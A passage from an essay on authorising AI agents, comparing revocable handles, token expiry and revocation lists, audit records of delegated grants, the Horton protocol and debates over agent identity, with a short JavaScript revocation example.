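But she can pick only resources that she already knows the task will need. If she asks the agent to remove the databases her team no longer uses, finding them is part of the work she wanted to delegate. If the agent stopped to have her pick each of 40 resources, at 5 units per interruption, the total would be 200 units. An overnight task would stop at the first pick and wait until morning. She could also pick the wrong item, especially if the list shows only names.

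A harness can require the user to pick the resource for deletions and payments, and let the agent interpret the user's references when it only needs to read something. For the clean-up task, the agent could prepare one list of databases to delete, with their details, and Ana could take out any that should stay. This would interrupt her once instead of 40 times, although she might approve a long list as hastily as a series of prompts.

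In 9.6% of the runs where Ji and colleagues gave the target's full name and the agent acted, the agent still affected something other than the target. The harness should therefore enforce the user's choice with a handle to the target.

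## Revoking and recording authority passed with requests

After a harness gives an agent a handle to delete `db-204`, Ana may change her mind, or an auditor may ask who used the handle and why. With an access list, an administrator can remove the agent's account, and the log shows what each account did. Handles can also support revocation and an audit trail if a designer builds them in, though critics of capabilities long argued that handles allow neither.

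### A handle with an off switch

Suppose Alice holds a handle to Carol, a program that stores files, and wants to lend Bob access. Miller and colleagues describe how she can do this and still take the access back:

1. Alice creates two linked objects, a forwarder and a switch. The switch holds her handle to Carol.
2. She gives Bob the forwarder and keeps the switch.
3. When Bob sends a request to the forwarder, it goes through the switch to Carol.
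4. To end Bob's access, Alice tells the switch to stop. It drops its handle to Carol, and the forwarder no longer leads anywhere.

Bob still has the forwarder, but it no longer works. If he passed it to Ted, Ted loses access too, even if Alice doesn't know Ted exists, because Bob never had a direct handle to pass on.

In JavaScript, an application could lend the `receipts` package its template reader this way:

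```js
function makeRevocable(target) {
  let current = target;
  return {
    forward: (...args) => {
      if (current === null) throw new Error("access revoked");
      return current(...args);
    },
    revoke: () => { current = null; }
  };
}

const template = makeRevocable(readTemplate);
makeReceipt(order, template.forward);
template.revoke();
```

The package can keep `template.forward` for as long as it likes, but after the last line it gets only an error.

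Miller and colleagues credit the method to Redell's (1974) thesis, *Naming and Protection in Extendible Operating Systems*. Redell called the intermediary a "caretaker" and described it as a standard "escape hatch" in protection systems, so the idea was probably older.

The method works only if Bob reaches Carol by sending messages and the forwarder can pass on any message. A program must also be able to stand in for the resource. Redell gives a segment of memory as an example that fails this condition. Programs use different instructions to read memory and to call another program, so Bob would have to change his code to use a caretaker. Each access would also take far longer than an ordinary read.

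Revocation doesn't recover data that Bob has already copied. He can also keep any direct handle that Carol returned to him, such as one to a particular file, unless the forwarder wraps those handles too.

Alice needs a separate forwarder for each person whose access she might want to end individually. Redell also considered chains of links, where everyone who passes on access adds a link they can later weaken or cut. A request gets only the rights that every link allows. If Alice gives Bob read and write access and Bob gives Ted read access, Bob can cut off Ted alone, while Alice can cut off both. Users who built such chains themselves could accidentally create endless loops, and the system had to follow the whole chain at each access. Redell therefore proposed building revocation into the operating system. The later systems KeyKOS and EROS made most accesses fast by storing the result of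 following a chain.

### Expiry, single use and revocation lists

Alice cannot directly switch off a signed token that a service checks offline. Instead, the issuer can limit how long the token lasts or how often it can be used, or the service can check a list of cancelled tokens.

Suppose Ana approves a list of 40 databases to delete, and her agent passes the job to another company's agent, which deletes one every 30 seconds. After four minutes, when eight databases are gone, Ana notices a mistake in the list and cancels the task, but the other agent never receives the cancellation. The table shows how many more databases that agent can delete.

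| Arrangement | Further deletions |
|---|---|
| One token that lasts an hour | 32 |
| One token that lasts five minutes | up to 2 |
| 40 single-use tokens, issued together, that last an hour | 32 |
| Single-use tokens, issued one at a time | up to 1 |
| One-hour token, with a revocation list checked at every call | none, unless one is in progress |
| One-hour token, with a revocation list downloaded every minute | up to 2 |

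The five-minute token has one minute left when Ana cancels, which is enough for two deletions. But the full 20-minute job needs four such tokens. The agent has to contact the issuer for each new one, and the issuer has to check that the task is still active. If the issuer renews tokens without checking, the short lifetime gives no protection.

The March version of Niyikiza's token proposal leaves out revocation of individual tokens so that services can work without contacting the issuer. It describes a short lifetime as "operationally equivalent to revocation for most threat models". That is reasonable when misuse takes time, but a short lifetime doesn't help when one call does all the damage. The agent that deleted PocketOS's database needed only one request, so a five-minute token would have been as dangerous as a permanent one.

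Single-use tokens can't be used twice, but an agent can still use any it has left after the task has been cancelled. The service must also keep a record of the tokens it has accepted. Niyikiza's design lets the service skip this record for harmless reads, where someone who copies a proof can reuse it for about 60 seconds.

A revocation list is the fastest way to cancel a token, but the service has to store the list and keep it up to date. In *Delegated Authority Problem Space Report*, an early draft from the Decentralized Identity Foundation, Bucci, Caballero and colleagues recommend also giving tokens an expiry time, so the service can remove cancelled tokens from the list once they expire. If a service cancels 100 tokens an hour and every token lasts an hour, the list never needs more than about 100 entries. With 30-day tokens, it could reach 72,000 entries.

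Even if a service checks the revocation list at every call, a race remains, since Ana can cancel a token just as the service starts a deletion. Bucci and Lu, in *Governance of Delegated Authority Problem Space Report*, call this race unavoidable and want operators to decide beforehand whether such an action may finish. They also want the service to refuse a request if it can't complete the check. Under that rule, a failure of the revocation service will stop legitimate work too.

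### What the logs leave out

An access-list system can easily record that Carol's account read a file at 14:05, but it is less likely to record why Carol had access. Bucci and colleagues give the example of Bob asking Alice to add Carol to a file's access list. The log shows that Alice made the change, but not that Bob asked for it. If Carol misuses the file and Alice doesn't know her, Alice has nobody to hold responsible. If Bob later asks Alice to remove Carol, Alice has to rely on memory to judge whether he has the right to ask.

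A chain of signed tokens shows that Alice gave access to Bob and that Bob gave some of it to Carol, but it may identify each of them only by a public key. A plain handle, such as an open file descriptor, doesn't record who passed the access along or who received it.

A log can combine both kinds of information if every grant has its own handle and its own record. Suppose Ana's clean-up agent asks a backup company's agent to copy `db-204` before the deletion. The harness records two grants:

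| Grant | Derived from | Holder | Responsible party | Permits |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `g-1` | Ana's access | clean-up agent | Ana | reading and deleting `db-204` |
| `g-2` | `g-1` | backup company's agent | the backup company | reading `db-204` |

Both records also include the ID of Ana's request. The database service only has to log that someone used `g-2` to read `db-204` at 14:05. An auditor can trace `g-2` back to `g-1` and to Ana's request. If the copy leaks, Ana's company knows which firm to question and can cancel `g-2` without stopping the clean-up. If both agents had used Ana's token, the log would attribute both of their actions to Ana.

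The harness should fill in these records itself, because a model could enter the wrong request or party. Even a correct record shows only which grant an agent used, not what led the agent to use it.

Bucci and colleagues point out that banning delegation can make the log less accurate, because when people get around the ban, actions are logged under the wrong party.

### The Horton protocol

In *Delegating Responsibility in Digital Systems* (2007), Miller, Donnelley and Karp published a worked design for recording whom to blame for an action. They accepted that capability systems couldn't do this, and called it the only criticism of those systems that nobody had refuted. Their protocol, Horton, adds this information without changing the programs that make the requests.

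Suppose Alice's program asks Bob's program to edit a wiki page that Carol hosts. Alice already has separate connections to Bob and to Carol. Horton then works like this:

1. Alice's program sends the request, with its reference to the page, to a proxy that Alice keeps for dealing with Bob.
2. The proxy asks Carol's side to create a new entry point to the page for Bob.
3. Carol's side labels the entry point "Bob", seals it so that only Bob can open it, and returns it to the proxy.
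4. The proxy logs that Bob is responsible for carrying out the request, and sends him the request and the sealed entry point.
5. Bob's side logs that Alice is responsible for the request. It opens the entry point with Carol's participation, puts a proxy labelled "Carol" in front of it, and passes that proxy to Bob's program.

Alice could have given Bob her own entry point, but Carol would then have blamed her for his edits. The seal prevents Alice from using Bob's entry point and framing him. Opening the seal also requires Carol's participation, so Alice can't give Bob a fake page and claim it is Carol's.

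If Bob vandalises the page, Carol can shut off every entry point labelled "Bob" without affecting Alice's access. Bob can likewise stop using Carol's services if they prove unreliable. A label identifies whoever holds a particular cryptographic key, but Bob can edit the page because he holds an entry point, not because of the label.

Carol may know Bob only as someone Alice introduced. Until Carol has reason to think "Bob" isn't Alice under another name, she should hold Alice responsible for what he does. Carol also has to take part in every introduction. Miller, Donnelley and Karp provided implementations in Java and in E, a capability-based programming language, but reported no performance measurements or experience with real users.

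The records can also be disputed, because each party keeps its own. *A thought on principals* (Shapiro, 2025) started a discussion of auditing in capability systems. In that discussion, Miller said that Horton supports auditing if the auditor is willing to believe the parties' records. Karp described an alternative based on signed certificates, each of which names its recipient in a way that makes sense to the issuer. If Alice delegates to Bob and Bob delegates to Dave, Alice holds Bob responsible for Dave's actions, and Bob holds Dave responsible. Alice doesn't have to know who Dave is. Miller thought this was close to Horton's logic, but neither he nor Karp had shown that the two were equivalent.

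Karp also argued that if people can share credentials, a log can establish only whom to hold responsible for an action, not who performed it. Ben Laurie, another participant, agreed but said that auditors don't want to hear this. Someone else objected to being blamed for what a thief does with stolen credentials. An access-list log has the same problem, since it records the account and not the person who used it.

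### Whether agents also need identities

Deville and several contributors from the Decentralized Identity Foundation argue in *Authorising Autonomous Agents at Scale* that handles aren't enough for agents, even with good records. Agents may last only 15 minutes, start other agents, and work with companies that have no agreement with their owner's company. According to Deville, a service therefore needs to know which agent is acting, who started it, and whom it represents, as well as what it may do.

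One of Deville's arguments concerns missing attribution. If 100 employees each use three AI products, and each product starts ten agents a day, 3,000 agents a day act under the employees' accounts. If one leaks private data, the log may show only the employee's name, and cancelling the shared token may stop other agents too. This is a good argument against shared credentials but a weaker one against handles, since a separate handle for each agent would also distinguish them.

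Another argument uses an example from Gallo in which an agent books a rental car to match a flight, and the flight then becomes unavailable. The agent has to cancel the car, but nobody could have given it a handle for that booking in advance, and permission to cancel any booking would be too broad. Deville proposes that the rental company issue a signed credential with the booking, `CAR-123`. The credential lets only the agent that made the booking cancel it, and only until pickup.

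Most of this solution is an ordinary handle, which the rental company creates once the booking exists. The identity condition protects against theft of the credential. But if the agent has stopped running by the time the flight falls through, its replacement can't cancel the car unless the rental company accepts it as the same agent. Without the condition, the first agent could have passed the handle to its replacement.

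Zagidulin raises a "patchwork problem", in which an agent combines permissions from different sources in ways nobody intended. For example, it might read a confidential file with one handle and publish the contents with another. An identifier could help a service notice that both handles belong to the same agent, but something still has to check the combination. Bucci and colleagues describe a way to do this without identity, in which the issuer fixes the set of permissions at the start of a task and the agent can't combine them with others.

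Bucci and colleagues think that identity is most useful for finding a responsible party, and that a service deciding on access should instead ask for proof that the request is authorised. They compare an agent to a car that hits yours at a traffic light, where you want to know who was driving rather than the car's serial number. An agent that exists for seconds can't be held responsible, and a malicious owner who loses one agent can start another.

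Their draft also acknowledges a problem with this position. Nobody can punish an agent, which removes most of the benefit of tracking its responsibility. Blaming the person who wrote the prompt may be unfair if the prompt was harmless and the agent chose a harmful way to carry it out. Handles and identifiers don't settle whether the user, the agent's provider or the model's developer is responsible for such an action, so organisations have to agree on that in advance.

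The two positions are compatible in practice. A service can use the handle to decide whether to allow each request, log the responsible party, and use that record to decide whether to give that party more handles. Carol does this when she shuts off Bob. Checking identity at every request makes sense when the owner doesn't want a handle to be transferred, but it requires more infrastructure. Deville acknowledges that registering identifiers, checking for revocation, and managing keys for short-lived agents all add overhead.

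### Systems that combine the two

Amazon's widely used pre-signed URLs partly combine authority carried in a request with account permissions, since each URL works only while the account that signed it still has permission. But the URL identifies the signer, not the person using it. If an invoice service signs URLs for all its customers with one account, the signature can't show which customer downloaded a file. Removing that account's access would disable every customer's URLs.

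Systems designed for agents are newer. KYA-OS adds a layer for identity and delegation to MCP, according to the Decentralized Identity Foundation's *Why We Brought KYA-OS (formerly MCP-I) to DIF*. The identity-verification company Vouched donated the specification to the foundation in March 2026. KYAPay gives agents tokens for getting through login and checkout pages, and the foundation's *Building the Agentic Economy* describes a prototype launch with Visa's commerce programme. Both accounts come from an organisation that promotes such standards, and a prototype provides little evidence about long-term use.

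There seems to be no published record of how often combined systems fail in use, but one serious weakness is predictable. Anyone who steals an issuer's signing key can create valid tokens for anything the issuer could authorise. The log would then show a complete chain of grants, starting with one the issuer never made.
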